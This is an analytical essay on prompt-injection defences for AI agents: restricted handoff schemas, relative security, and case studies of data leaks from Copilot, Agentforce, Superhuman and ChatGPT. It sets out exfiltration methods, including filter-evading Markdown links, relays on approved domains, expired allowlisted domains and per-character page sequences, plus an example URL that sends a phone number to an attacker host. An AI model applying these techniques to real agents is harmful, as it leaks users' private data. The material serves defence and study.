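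They argue that 45% is still useful because Claude 3.7 Sonnet scored 48% on SWE-bench Lite without a defence. But that model dates from early 2025. A fairer comparison is with GPT-5.2's own 68.3% without the defence, which means the defence prevents about one in three successful repairs. The defence also requires several models instead of one, and the developers needed considerable testing to find a schema that worked.

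Some of the same researchers later tried letting a little text through. In *Twin Agent*, Hu, Jacob and colleagues (2026) argue that fixed handoffs often lose too much information and need redesigning for every task. In their system, an agent that reads the untrusted text also sees what the privileged agent has done so far, and sends that agent a short hint about the next step. Software cuts off or blocks any hint that is too long, and a detector checks each one for injections. The researchers report that this stops attacks while keeping task success high on both SWE-bench Lite and AgentDojo.

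However, limiting the length of text gives a weaker guarantee than banning text. Hu and colleagues assume that a short injection is unlikely to take over one of the latest models, so their defence is probabilistic. A long task also involves many hints, and an attacker might spread an instruction across several of them. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues make a similar compromise for a coding agent that reads outside documentation. They suggest passing on only a formal description of each function, with names of at most 30 characters. A name of that length can still contain a short English command, with underscores between the words.

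### Can a number carry an instruction?

The argument that numbers cannot carry a command is convincing for the shopping agent. Two scores from 0 to 10 allow 11 × 11 = 121 combinations, or about 6.9 bits (log₂ 121), roughly the capacity of a single printed character.

The argument depends on the range being limited, though. If `review_support` had no upper limit, an attacker could write each letter of a message as two digits, from 01 for A to 26 for Z. A 100-digit number could then spell out 50 letters. The privileged model receives the number as a string of digits, so it could in principle recognize the code, translate it and obey the message. Most models would probably just treat the number as a strange score, but the defence would then depend on how the model behaves, which the handoff is meant to avoid.

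Decimals need a limit for the same reason, since many digits can follow the decimal point. Rounding a score between 0 and 10 to one decimal place leaves 101 possible values. Some providers do not enforce number ranges during generation, so a validator should check them before the privileged model receives the handoff.

A list can carry a message even if every item in it is harmless. The calendars have 63 one-hour slots, nine a day for seven days, which is enough to give every letter and digit its own slot. A list of 40 proposed times could therefore spell out a 40-character message. Jacob and colleagues do not state their cap on list length, but a limit of five proposed times would let the list carry about 30 bits, or five characters in this code.

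The bug-fixing handoff can carry much more data. In a project of 2,000 files with 1,000 lines each, a single code region can carry about 33 bits, so ten regions could hold about 50 characters. A low limit matters most for this agent because its privileged model can run commands.

The experiments did not test encoded instructions. Each agent faced one fixed injection in plain language, which could not have passed through the handoff. The 0% results confirm that the agents were set up correctly, but the argument that they would also block encoded instructions depends on the schema's limits.

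### False values that pass every check

An attacker who can't send instructions through the handoff can still choose what it contains. Jacob and colleagues acknowledge that their method does not prevent misinformation, and they exclude misinformation from their definition of prompt injection.

In the bug-fixing agent, a hijacked quarantined model could report a fault in login code that works correctly, and the privileged agent might weaken the code while trying to repair it. The injection could also make the judge pick the worst of the three plans, because the judge reads the same bug report. The final patch is free of injected instructions but may still be harmful, although Jacob and colleagues describe it as guaranteed to be safe.

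Attackers can also lie without an injection, for instance by filing a false bug report. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues compare injections with such lies to judge how much an attacker can gain through a restricted field. In one of their examples, an agent looks for invoices to send to the accounting department, and a separate model answers yes or no to whether each file is an invoice. An injection can make the model answer yes for the attacker's file, but the attacker could get the same answer by replacing the file with a real invoice.

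This is a sensible standard, although an injection can make a lie more effective. It can make the quarantined model give a suspicious review a relevance of 10 every time, when the model might otherwise have given it a 2.

The shopping agent limits the effect of false scores by taking the median, the middle value when the scores are in order. Suppose eight honest reviews give a product support scores of 2, 2, 3, 3, 3, 4, 4 and 5. Their median is 3 and their mean is 3.25. Here is what happens as an attacker adds reviews that score 10:

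| Fake reviews | Median | Mean |
|---|---|---|
| 0 | 3 | 3.25 |
| 1 | 3 | 4.0 |
| 3 | 4 | 5.1 |
| 9 | 10 | 6.8 |

One fake review has no effect on the median here. As long as fake reviews are a minority, the median cannot go above the highest honest score or below the lowest. Once they are a majority, the attacker can set it to anything. The quarantined model must also read each review separately, because otherwise an injection in one review could change the scores of the honest ones.

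The median doesn't protect a product with a single review, which is one reason to tell the privileged agent how many reviews there are. The two medians are calculated separately, so a review with a relevance of 0 still counts fully towards the support score. Dropping irrelevant reviews before taking the medians would fix this for honest off-topic reviews but not for injected ones, which can still get a relevance of 10.

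Taking the median works for reviews because many people answer the same question independently. A bug report usually has one author, and each person is the only one who can say when they are free to meet. Developers of bug-fixing and scheduling agents have to catch false values in other ways, for example by running the project's tests or having a person review the repair.

### What an injection may reveal

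The calendar agent has to reveal something about the user's calendar to arrange a meeting. A rule that nothing the attacker sees may depend on private data would forbid this normal work. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) proposes the more practical rule that an injection should reveal nothing the agent would not reveal without one.

To make this precise, Dongol compares the real agent with a reference agent. Both follow the same plan and the same security checks, but the reference agent's model never obeys untrusted text. Leaving aside timing and the agent's memory, let O(a, s) be what the attacker observes from the real agent when the attacker's input is a and the secret is s. Let R(a, s) be the same for the reference agent. The real agent is relatively secure if, for any two secrets s₁ and s₂,

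if O(a, s₁) ≠ O(a, s₂) for some input a, then R(b, s₁) ≠ R(b, s₂) for some input b.

In other words, if an injection lets the attacker tell two secrets apart, some input must also do so when the model ignores injections. The inputs a and b can differ. One of Dongol's examples is an assistant that sends the user's calendar to anyone who asks for a meeting. The rule allows an injection that makes the assistant send the calendar, because an ordinary meeting request would do the same. The injection breaks the rule if it also makes the assistant send a password reset code, because no ordinary request would reveal the code.

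The basic rule can allow an injection to reveal much more than honest use would. Suppose an agent tells people whether their guess at a four-digit code is right, and an injection makes it send the whole code. An honest guess at one of any two codes would tell them apart, so the agent still counts as relatively secure. Yet an honest guess rules out only one code in 10,000, while the injection reveals the code at once. Dongol's stricter version, uniform relative security, requires b to depend only on a, not on the secrets. A single guess can't distinguish most pairs of codes, so the agent fails this stricter test.

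Dongol used the proof assistant Isabelle/HOL to prove results for 25 small example agents. The calendar agent from Jacob and colleagues is not among them, but the same reasoning applies to a single exchange of emails. Whatever the attacker writes, the quarantined model returns a list of times. If the attacker had instead sent an ordinary email proposing those times, the privileged model would have received the same list and had the same information for its reply. The times in that ordinary email depend only on the attacker's original message, because the quarantined model has not seen the calendar. The injection therefore reveals nothing more than the ordinary email would, even by the stricter rule.

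Ordinary emails still reveal some of the user's schedule. If the attacker proposes Friday at 15:00 and the agent accepts, the attacker learns that the user is free then. By proposing more times, the attacker could work out much of the user's week. The experiment would not have counted this as a leak, because its test covered only the marker phrase in event descriptions.

A developer has to limit such disclosure separately, for example by allowing only a few replies with three proposed times each. There are 39,711 ways to choose three slots out of 63, so the times in one reply reveal at most about 15 bits. Dongol proves that if an agent is relatively secure, any such limit that holds for the reference agent also holds for the real one.

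The guarantee would fail if the quarantined model could read the calendar. The model could then choose times that encode a client's name, and the agent's reply might reveal those times. The general method of Jacob and colleagues allows this because it lets any information reach the quarantined model. Their calendar agent avoids the problem by giving that model only the email thread.

In one of Dongol's examples, a quarantined model reads the user's private notes and gives an answer, and the agent sends one of two fixed public messages depending on that answer. Neither message contains private data, but the choice between them reveals one bit of information about the notes.

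Relative security also covers only secrets. An injection that makes the shopping agent buy the wrong product can satisfy the rule because it doesn't have to reveal anything. Dongol leaves such attacks out of scope, so the limits on actions and false values need separate checks.

The calendar agent's `meeting_description` field is another weak point. The privileged model can't read this text during the email exchange, but the agent saves it in the user's calendar, which the privileged model can read. An injection in the description could therefore take effect when the agent arranges its next meeting. The experiment would have missed this because it tested each email thread separately.

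Dongol's guarantees assume that attackers cannot write to trusted sources, so a calendar that contains attackers' text does not count as trusted. For a similar booking agent, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues suggest hiding event descriptions. The privileged model can find a free time using only 63 yes/no values that show which slots are taken.

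## Links and images that passed the filters in Copilot, Agentforce and Superhuman

Workplace assistants such as Microsoft 365 Copilot can't be limited to numbers and fixed lists, because their users want written answers with links and sometimes pictures. Their developers let the model write freely and use code to check the addresses in its answer. Researchers got past such checks in four cases, all of which the vendors have since repaired. The flaws were EchoLeak and SearchLeak in Copilot, ForcedLeak in Salesforce's Agentforce, and an unnamed one in the email program Superhuman.

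In all four cases, the model followed an injected instruction and put private data into an image's address, which the user's browser then requested. All three products had a CSP that limited where images could come from, but each time the researchers found an approved domain through which the data could leave. Copilot also cleaned its answers before or during display, and the researchers got past that too.

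### A link format that the filter missed

Copilot answers employees' questions using their company's emails, files and chats. Outsiders can't open it, but they can email an employee. Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*, describes how a single email was enough to steal data without the employee clicking anything. When the employee later asked Copilot a question and it retrieved that email, the prompt injection in the email made Copilot write the most sensitive details it could see into a web address.

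Microsoft used a classifier to look for prompt injections in incoming text. Ravia's team at Aim Labs got past it by wording the instructions as if they were meant for the employee, without mentioning an AI. The next safeguard was ordinary, deterministic code that removed links to outside websites from Copilot's answers before the user could click them.

Copilot writes its answers in Markdown, a simple notation for formatted text that offers several ways to write the same link. The most common is the inline form:

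```
See the [travel policy](https://intranet.example/travel).
```

The reference form puts the address elsewhere in the text:

```
See the [travel policy][1].

[1]: https://intranet.example/travel
```

Inline and reference links in Markdown appear on screen as the same clickable words. Copilot's filter removed outside links in the inline form but missed the reference form and its variants. It had the same gap for images, which are written like links with an exclamation mark in front.

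If a deterministic filter misses a link format, it will miss that format every time, unlike a classifier, which may miss one malicious email and catch the next. An attacker who finds the gap can rely on it until someone fixes the code.

The mistake is to search the text for patterns that look like links. A parser instead reads the whole text by the rules of the notation, as the program that displays it does. A safer filter works in three steps:

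1. It parses the complete answer into a tree, in which every link and image is a separate item with its own destination.
2. It checks each destination and removes any item whose destination is not allowed.
3. It builds the displayed page from the checked tree and throws away the model's original text.

The third step prevents two programs from parsing the same text differently. If the filter only approves the text and a different parser then displays it, that parser may find a link that the filter missed. Many Markdown programs also accept raw HTML, so the filter has to parse or remove that too.

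*EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) reports that Microsoft now also strips reference-style links and images from outside content before Copilot reads it. This makes the attack harder, but the output still needs checking, because an injection could describe the notation in ordinary words and the model could then write the link itself.

Copilot normally refers to the emails it has used, which might have alerted the employee to the attacker's email. But the injection included an instruction not to mention that email, and Copilot followed it. A list of sources is reliable only if trusted code compiles it from records of what the model received.

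### Approved services that fetch other addresses

The link format that the filter missed could leak data if the employee clicked the link, because Copilot's CSP restricted which images a page could load but not which links a user could follow. To leak data without a click, Ravia's team needed the browser to load an image, but the CSP blocked images from unknown domains.

The image policy that Ravia reproduces has 29 different entries. Eleven are wildcards, which approve every subdomain of a domain, and 14 entries appear twice, so the list had probably grown without much review. The researchers searched the approved domains for a service that would fetch some other address on request. An invented example shows how such a relay works:

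`https://approved.example/preview?url=https://attacker.example/555-0142`

1. The browser finds `approved.example` in the policy and sends it the request.
2. A program at `approved.example` reads the second address and fetches it from its own server, perhaps to prepare a preview.
3. The server at `attacker.example` receives that second request and logs the phone number in the path.

Security engineers call this server-side request forgery. A CSP can't prevent it, because the browser never contacts `attacker.example`.

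Ravia's team first found a relay in SharePoint, Microsoft's file-sharing service, but it worked only if the employee had accepted an invitation to the attacker's site. They then found one in Microsoft Teams that needed no action from the employee.

When an approved server redirects an image request, the browser checks the new destination against the CSP and blocks a redirect directly to `attacker.example`. A filter for clickable links checks only the first address, not any address it redirects to. A program that fetches pages from a company's server needs its own check at every redirect.

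A developer should therefore assume that data can leak through any approved domain that relays requests. One remedy is to keep images on a domain that serves only fixed files. If the company needs the relay, its own code can sign each address the relay may fetch, so that the relay rejects any address written by the model.

### Cleaning the answer after it appears

In June 2026 the security firm Varonis disclosed a second way to steal data through Copilot. Its report *SearchLeak* (2026) describes a flaw in Copilot Enterprise Search, which searches a company's emails, meetings and files. A link to this service can include a search query. Copilot treated the query as instructions, so an attacker could put a prompt injection in a link and send it to an employee. The link led to a genuine Microsoft address, so ordinary phishing filters were unlikely to block it.

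One click made Copilot search the employee's mailbox and write an HTML image whose URL contained an email's subject line. Subject lines often include one-time security codes, so even a short leak can be harmful.

Microsoft's safeguard was to wrap Copilot's answer in a code block, which makes the browser show HTML as plain characters. Unlike the link filter in EchoLeak, this does not depend on recognizing dangerous formats. But it ran too late. Chat programs usually stream an answer, displaying each part as the model writes it, and this is what happened:

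1. Copilot wrote the image as part of its answer.
2. The browser displayed the image and requested its address.
3. Copilot finished the answer.
4. Microsoft's code wrapped the answer in a code block.

The data had left at the second step. Programmers call this a race condition, an error in which the result depends on which of two events happens first.

The CSP still blocked direct requests to the attacker's server. Varonis got around it with Bing's search-by-image feature, which takes an image's URL and has Bing's servers fetch the image. Bing's domain was on the approved list because it belongs to Microsoft. It was also on the list that Ravia's report had reproduced a year earlier.

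Varonis recommends cleaning the output when it is displayed. The simplest way is to hold the whole answer until the validator finishes, but then the user waits longer for the first words. A developer can avoid most of that wait by streaming the answer as plain text, then adding the links and images after the validator approves them.

Approving each link as it arrives is harder, because a reference-style link can have its address on the last line of the answer, and the validator can't check the address before that line arrives. A validator that releases text early must therefore leave such a link inactive.

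The same output may also appear in more than one place, and a check in the chat window doesn't cover text that an email program displays later. Copilot Cowork, a Microsoft agent that works with a user's files, could send emails to the user's own inbox without approval. Willison explains in *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”* that these emails could contain external images, which loaded when the user opened the message. An attacker could use these images to obtain download links for the user's files.

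### Microsoft's account of its deterministic blocking

Microsoft says it designs its products assuming that some injections will succeed, and compares this with operating system protections that keep undiscovered memory errors from becoming working attacks. After Johann Rehberger, an independent security researcher, reported a leak through Markdown images, Microsoft blocked that technique deterministically. It says it also looks for variants of each reported flaw, and that it took similar steps against certain untrusted links.

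Where Microsoft can't sufficiently block or detect a harmful action, it asks the user to approve the action. For example, Copilot can draft an email in Outlook, but the user has to send it. Microsoft also says in its Copilot documentation that it removes outbound data routes the product doesn't need.

Deterministic blocking is a sound approach despite the two Copilot flaws, which show how much depends on the details. Microsoft had blocked outside links, but only in the formats its filter recognized. Its code block would have made the HTML image harmless if it had been in place from the first word. Microsoft also searched for variants after EchoLeak, but at least one relay on an approved domain, Bing's, still worked for Varonis.

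The emails from Copilot Cowork show a similar gap in the approval rule. Images in an email can send requests to any server, even if the email looks harmless because it goes only to the user's own inbox.

### An approved domain that anyone could buy

ForcedLeak was an attack on Agentforce, Salesforce's platform for AI agents that work with customer records. Companies can connect these records to a public web form where potential customers leave their details. An attacker could enter a prompt injection in the form, and it took effect when an employee later asked Agentforce to handle the new entry. The attack needed neither a link format that the filter missed nor a relay.

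Noma Labs' *ForcedLeak* (2025) describes the form's name and email fields, which were limited to 40 or 80 characters, as too short for an injection. The description field accepted 42,000 characters. A much lower limit on that field would have made the attack harder to write.

Salesforce's Content Security Policy (CSP) allowed images from 22 domains. One of them, `my-salesforce-cms.com`, had expired, and the researchers bought it for $5. The policy still allowed the domain, so browsers sent the researchers any data that Agentforce had put in the address of an image there. In the demonstration, the data was the email addresses of a company's potential customers.

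An allowlist identifies destinations by domain name, and a domain can change owners while the list stays the same. The expired domain was hard to spot because the list also included the similar names `my-salesforce.com` and `salesforce-experience.com`. A company can have a program check the registration of every approved domain daily and warn staff well before one expires. The company should also delete entries that no product uses. Subdomains need the same care, because one may still point to a cloud server that the company has given up and someone else can now rent.

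The list also approved every subdomain of `amazonaws.com`, where customers of Amazon's cloud service get addresses for their own servers and storage. An attacker with an Amazon account might not have needed to buy an expired domain.

Salesforce regained the expired domain and began restricting the URLs in agents' answers. TechNadu's *Salesforce to Enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI* reports that administrators had to list every outside domain their agents needed or risk disruption when the new rule took effect. PromptArmor's *One key way Salesforce mitigates AI risk* explains that the Salesforce web app now replaces any unlisted URL in Markdown, HTML or CSS with a fixed placeholder before it displays the answer.

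This rule is stricter than Copilot's old link filter because it removes addresses by default, whatever notation surrounds them. It still depends on code that recognizes every form an address can take. It also doesn't cover the tools an agent can call. PromptArmor recommends other defences for those, such as human approval.

The repair also leaves the choice of domains to each customer. PromptArmor warns administrators against wildcards that cover sites where anyone can publish. It also advises them to block images from listed domains unless they need them, which Salesforce lets them do with a separate permission. Blocking images stops a domain from receiving data automatically, but it can still receive data if a user clicks a link.

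### An approved domain that stores what it receives

Superhuman's CSP allowed `docs.google.com`, which hosts Google Forms. Anyone can create a form there. A form can accept answers in a URL, so requesting the URL submits them.

PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* describes an attack in which a user asks the assistant to summarize recent mail, including an unopened email from the attacker. A prompt injection in that email makes the assistant write an image link whose URL contains the contents of other emails and submits them to the attacker's Google Form. When the browser tries to load the image, it sends the data to the form, where the attacker can read it.

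In one test, a single answer leaked parts of more than 40 emails. PromptArmor also obtained the full text of several messages containing financial, legal and medical information.

This flaw is harder to find in a review than an expired domain or a relay, because the domain belonged to a reputable company and the form worked as Google intended. A reviewer has to check whether any service on the domain lets a stranger store or read the contents of a request. For a large domain, that means knowing every product its owner offers there, including any added later.

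Other developers have made the same mistake:

- In 2023 Google's chatbot Bard accepted images from any Google subdomain. Willison, in *Hacking Google Bard*, notes that one of these subdomains let anyone run their own program, which could receive the stolen data.
- In November 2025 Antigravity, Google's programming tool, had a default allowlist that included `webhook.site`, a service that records incoming requests for whoever set up the address.
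- In April 2026 PromptArmor got emails out of OpenAI's Codex agent through a Google form, three months after the Superhuman flaw became public. OpenAI has since repaired this, according to PromptArmor's *Codex Exfiltrates Connector Data*.

The uploads from Claude Cowork to an attacker's Anthropic account worked in a similar way. In each case, the developer approved a domain because of who ran it and overlooked what strangers could do there.

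Administrators can easily repeat the error. Salesforce's *Add Trusted URLs for Agentforce Coworker (Beta)* uses `https://docs.google.com` as its example of a trusted address, so that the assistant can display Google Drive data. Trusting that domain is reasonable for links to documents, but if the administrator also allows images from it, a form hosted there could collect data without the user clicking anything.

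Superhuman had two other flaws that removing Google's domain from the CSP would not have fixed. Superhuman Go, its agent for web pages and connected accounts, accepted images from the attacker's own domain. The agent in Superhuman Mail could open any web address to look up information, so an injection could make it open one with private data attached. Grammarly, which belongs to the same company, also had the image flaw, but its assistant appeared to read only the open document and the user's questions, so it would seldom have had access to both private data and an attacker's text at once.

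### Severity, repair times and real-world use

The Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS) is the usual measure of a flaw's severity. Its scores run from 0 to 10 and reflect how easily an attacker can use the flaw and how much harm can follow.

| Flaw | Repaired | Details published | CVSS score | Known real-world use |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak | May 2025 | June 11, 2025 | 9.3 | None |
| ForcedLeak | September 8, 2025 | September 25, 2025 | 9.4 | Salesforce declined to say |
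| Superhuman | December 8, 2025 to January 11, 2026 | January 12, 2026 | None given | None reported |
| SearchLeak | By June 4, 2026 | June 15, 2026 | 6.5 | None |

The severity scores are a poor guide to which leak was worse. Microsoft gave EchoLeak 9.3, but the US National Vulnerability Database gave it 7.5, according to GCVE's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2025). Both agreed that the attack was easy and exposed a lot of private data, but Microsoft also counted effects beyond Copilot and a small risk that an attacker could alter data.

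Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026) gives SearchLeak a score of 6.5, which is medium severity. The national database gave EchoLeak 7.5. The two flaws are scored the same way except that SearchLeak requires the user to click once, which accounts for the whole difference. Microsoft still rated SearchLeak critical on its own scale. The Hacker News' *One-Click Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Could Have Let Attackers Steal Emails* (2026) reported that the national database also gave SearchLeak 7.5, but The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox* found 6.5 in both Microsoft's record and the database's.

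Repair times ranged from about five weeks to about eight months. Ravia's team reported EchoLeak in January 2025, about four months before the full repair. Salesforce began enforcing its new rule 42 days after Noma Labs' report, according to the dates in Security Affairs' *ForcedLeak flaw in Salesforce Agentforce exposes CRM data via Prompt Injection*. Superhuman received its report on a Friday night and switched off the vulnerable features the following Monday, then spent about five weeks on lasting repairs. Microsoft took from December 2025 to August 2026 to patch a later one-click flaw in the consumer version of Copilot, according to Varonis' *CoSnitch*.

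Superhuman's decision to turn off images in its assistant's answers before working on the parser and the allowlist is a good model. Turning off images inconveniences users little and immediately stops leaks through them, which gives engineers time for the other fixes. Microsoft repaired both Copilot flaws on its own servers, so customers had nothing to install. But it didn't explain in its SearchLeak notice what it had changed, so outsiders can't tell whether it fixed the late cleaning, the relay or both.

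The lack of known attacks is more reassuring for some of these flaws than for others. In EchoLeak and SearchLeak, the stolen data passed through Microsoft's own services, so the company could in principle look for it in its logs. In ForcedLeak and the Superhuman flaw, the user's browser sent the data straight to a domain the vendor did not run. The Register's *Prompt injection* (2025) reported that Salesforce declined to say whether anyone had abused ForcedLeak. Abuse seems unlikely, though, because the expired domain was still for sale when Noma Labs bought it.

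### Putting links in separate fields

A developer can avoid the first two failures, the missed link format and the late cleaning, by taking links out of the model's text altogether. The model then fills in a schema like this one:

```json
{
  "answer": "Your meeting with Dana is now on Friday.",
  "links": [
    {
      "label": "Calendar entry",
      "url": "https://calendar.example/event/1182"
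    }
  ]
}
```

Trusted code displays the `answer` field as plain text, so any Markdown link or HTML image in it appears as literal characters and the browser requests nothing. For the `links` field, the code waits until each item is complete, then creates a clickable link only if the host is on the allowlist.

The validator can't miss a link format, because the schema has only one field for addresses and the validator always checks it. The late cleaning can't recur either, because the program may stream `answer` as the model writes it, but an address becomes a link only after the validator approves it. The developer can add an `images` field with the same check if the product needs pictures, and leave it out otherwise.

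The protection fails if another part of the program adds links back. Many chat windows turn any text that looks like a web address into a link, and some messaging apps fetch a preview of the linked page. The developer has to switch off both features for the `answer` field.

Separate fields would not have prevented the other two failures. An address on `my-salesforce-cms.com` or `docs.google.com` is well formed, is in the correct field and has an approved host, so the validator would accept it. It would accept the relays in Teams and Bing for the same reason. If the schema has an `images` field, data can still leak without the user clicking anything.

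The remaining weakness is that the model writes the rest of the address. RFC 3986 allows 66 characters in an address without any special encoding, so 2,000 characters of free choice after the host can carry

2,000 × log₂ 66 ≈ 12,089 bits,

or about nine times as much as the 200-character note in the email sorter. Checking the host does not reduce this at all.

The schema can reduce the amount of data a link can leak by replacing `url` with a number that selects from a list of complete addresses. With 1,000 addresses to choose from, one link carries at most log₂ 1,000 ≈ 10 bits. Trusted code has to build the list without using the model, and the exact-address check in ChatGPT relies on a similar separation.

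## ChatGPT's rule: fetch automatically only addresses already public

OpenAI lets ChatGPT open an address automatically only if a separate program has already found that exact address on the public web. A list of 1,000 approved addresses wouldn't work, because people ask ChatGPT about pages from all over the web. Under this rule, a hijacked model can't automatically open an address with a stolen phone number added to it. But it can still send a message through its choice of public pages, because an attacker who owns those pages can see which ones it opens.

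### The first check, in December 2023

In April 2023 Johann Rehberger told OpenAI that a prompt injection could make ChatGPT leak a conversation through an image's address. OpenAI replied that this was a feature it did not plan to change, according to SecurityWeek's *Malicious GPT Can Phish Credentials, Exfiltrate Them to External Server*. About eight months later, OpenAI added a check called `url_safe`. When an answer contained an image, ChatGPT's web app sent the image's address to an OpenAI server, which returned "safe" or "unsafe". The app loaded only images marked safe. Willison (2023) found this "a bit weird", since OpenAI could simply have blocked images from outside domains.

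OpenAI did not publish the rules behind these verdicts, so outsiders could learn about `url_safe` only by trying addresses, whereas anyone can inspect a web page's CSP. Rehberger describes one such test in *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, on his blog Embrace The Red. He tried 36 image addresses on his own website, one for each letter and digit, and nine of them loaded. He couldn't tell why the image for "a" counted as safe and the one for "d" did not. In his demonstration, ChatGPT sent the word "hi" to his server, one letter per request.

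### Apps without the check and domains that always passed

The app on the user's device had to request the result of the URL check, so OpenAI had to add this step to each app separately. The iPhone app lacked it in December 2023, and new Mac and Android apps shipped without it in 2024, according to Embrace The Red's *Spyware Injection Into Your ChatGPT's Long-Term Memory (SpAIware)*.

By then ChatGPT also had a memory, which carries notes from one chat into later ones. Rehberger used an injection on a web page to store an instruction in that memory. From then on, the Mac app sent his server everything the user typed and every reply, even in new chats. In September 2024, OpenAI stopped the Mac app from loading the images that carried the data out, but injections could still write to the memory.

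Schwartzman (2024), in *Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection*, reported that an attacker could also steal personal data without using images, by having ChatGPT open a web address. At the time, Claude, Bing and Gemini could not open arbitrary addresses.

The check also allowed any address on certain domains, including `windows.net`, where anyone can rent Microsoft cloud storage and read the log of requests to it. Rehberger reported this bypass in October 2024, and it still worked when he prepared Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* in the summer of 2025. OpenAI blocked it around August 2025.

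ChatGPT also trusted `bing.com`. Links in Bing's search results start at a Bing address and forward the visitor to the site listed, so every site that Bing had indexed also had an address that ChatGPT accepted. The security firm Tenable reported this flaw in December 2024, and OpenAI had not yet fixed it when Tenable published *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* (2025).

### How the public index works

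In January 2026 OpenAI published a design that doesn't depend on trusting a domain. OpenAI gives two reasons for rejecting a list of trusted sites. One is redirects, which had already defeated `url_safe` through Bing. The other is that people visit far more sites than any list can hold. A strict list would therefore produce frequent warnings, and people would learn to click through them.

The new check works like this:

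1. A crawler, a program that explores the web as a search engine does, records the public addresses it finds. It has no access to users' conversations, accounts or personal data.
2. When ChatGPT is about to load a page or image automatically, ordinary code compares the full address with the crawler's records.
3. If the address matches a recorded one exactly, ChatGPT loads it without asking the user.
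4. If it doesn't match, the software either tells the model to try another website or shows the user a warning before opening the address.

An address the user types into the chat also counts as safe for that chat, as far as Embrace The Red could tell. According to OpenAI, by March 2026 the check also covered pages opened in its Atlas browser and searches by Deep Research, ChatGPT's agent for long research tasks.

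Exact matching stops ChatGPT from automatically fetching the address from the first section, `https://attacker.example/collect?data=555-0142`, because the crawler can have recorded it only if somebody published it. The attacker doesn't know the phone number yet, and the crawler has no access to the conversation that contains it. Moving the number to the path or a subdomain, or encoding it, doesn't help the attacker, because the resulting address isn't in the index either.

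Exact matching also solves most of the redirect problem, because the index would not contain the combined addresses that leaked data through the relays in Teams and Bing. A public address may still redirect to the attacker's server, but it can't carry anything the model added.

The guarantee depends on keeping the crawler separate from the model. If the crawler also recorded addresses from ChatGPT's own traffic, a hijacked model could get an address recorded by mentioning it once, then request it later.

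### Choosing among public addresses

An exact match shows that nobody wrote the user's secret into the address, but the model's choice of address can still depend on the secret. Suppose an attacker publishes 36 pages, one for each letter and digit, and waits for the crawler to record them. A hijacked model can then open the pages in the order that spells a client's name. Every address passes the check because it is already public, and the attacker reads the name from the order of requests in the server's log.

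If the attacker can see requests for M indexed addresses, each request carries at most

log₂ M bits.

With 36 pages that is log₂ 36 ≈ 5.2 bits, or one character. A 20-character name takes 20 requests and contains about 103 bits. More pages let the attacker send the same name in fewer requests:

| Prepared pages | Bits per request | Requests for a 20-character name |
|---|---|---|
| 36 (one per character) | 5.2 | 20 |
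| 1,296 (one per pair) | 10.3 | 10 |
| 4,096 | 12.0 | 9 |
| 46,656 (one per group of three) | 15.5 | 7 |

The 4,096 pages don't correspond to whole characters, so the model would have to convert the name into one large number first. Sending pairs is easier and takes only one more request.

Extra pages help the attacker little, because doubling their number adds only one bit per request. The rule is therefore a strong defence against bulk theft. With 36 fixed pages, leaking the 12,089 bits that 2,000 freely chosen characters can carry would take about 2,340 requests. The rule protects short secrets less well, since a six-digit security code takes only six requests and ten pages, and the answer to a yes/no question takes one request.

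Attackers may not need to prepare special pages, in which case nothing about the pages would look suspicious. Rehberger points out that a larger website or blog probably already has 36 indexed pages, and the injection can specify which page represents which character. He thinks a vocabulary of thousands of pages is possible.

Before OpenAI published its design, Tenable's *HackedGPT* (2025) had shown that this kind of leak worked. Bing's forwarding addresses can't be altered, so Tenable's researchers had Bing index one page for each letter. ChatGPT then leaked text by loading the matching addresses in order. In a separate test, the researchers got OpenAI's own crawler to record a site containing an injection, so getting into a crawler's index is not very difficult.

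### ZombieAgent

The security firm Radware used fixed addresses to steal data from connected email accounts. Its earlier attack, ShadowLeak, made Deep Research add private Gmail data to an address that the attacker supplied. OpenAI responded by allowing ChatGPT to open addresses only exactly as given, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *New Zero-Click Attack Lets ChatGPT User Steal Data*.

Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes how the firm's researcher Zvika Babo got around this rule. The attacker's email contained a ready-made list of addresses, one for each letter and digit and one for a space. When the user later asked ChatGPT to do something in Gmail, it read the email and opened the addresses that spelled out the private data. The requests came from OpenAI's servers, so the user could not see or stop them.

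Requests can arrive out of order, which would scramble the message, so Babo gave each character a separate address for every position. The address for "a" in first place differs from the one for "a" in second place, so the attacker can sort the requests afterwards. With 26 letters and 10 digits, a 20-character name needs 36 × 20 = 720 addresses.

Babo reported the flaw on September 26, 2025, and OpenAI fixed it on December 16, 81 days later. Radware published its report in January 2026 without explaining what OpenAI had changed. The index check would block the attack if the addresses existed only in the attacker's email, because the crawler never reads private mail. But the attack would still work against the published design if the attacker first published the 720 pages and got them indexed.

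### Caching, repeat limits and request caps

Rehberger suggests two ways to make such leaks harder. OpenAI could cache each page, keeping a copy for a few minutes and reusing it for repeat requests. Or it could refuse to open the same full address twice in one session. Either way, the attacker's server would receive only one request for each address, so if each letter had its own page, the name "hannah" would arrive as "han".

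Tenable noticed in its 2025 research that ChatGPT already seemed to do something similar. When asked about an address it had opened before, it answered without visiting the page again.

But neither remedy stops ZombieAgent's version of the attack, which uses a different address for each character in each position and so never needs to repeat one. For a 20-character name, caching forces the attacker to prepare 720 pages instead of 36, but the number of requests stays at 20.

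A cap on requests directly limits how much data can leak. In 2023 Rehberger proposed allowing only one or a few images per response. *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data* (2026) recommends limiting, for each tool, the volume of requests and how random their parameters look. The limit on randomness would do little here, because an attacker can choose fixed addresses that are short and ordinary.

If the attacker has M pages and the cap is r requests, the attacker gets about r × log₂ M bits. With 36 pages, five requests carry about 26 bits, or five letters or digits. With 4,096 pages, they carry 60 bits, more than the 53 bits of a card number. A developer should therefore choose the cap assuming that the attacker has thousands of pages.

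A cap that low would also hinder legitimate work, because a research agent may need to open dozens of pages. One compromise is to apply the cap only in chats where the model has read both private data and outside text.

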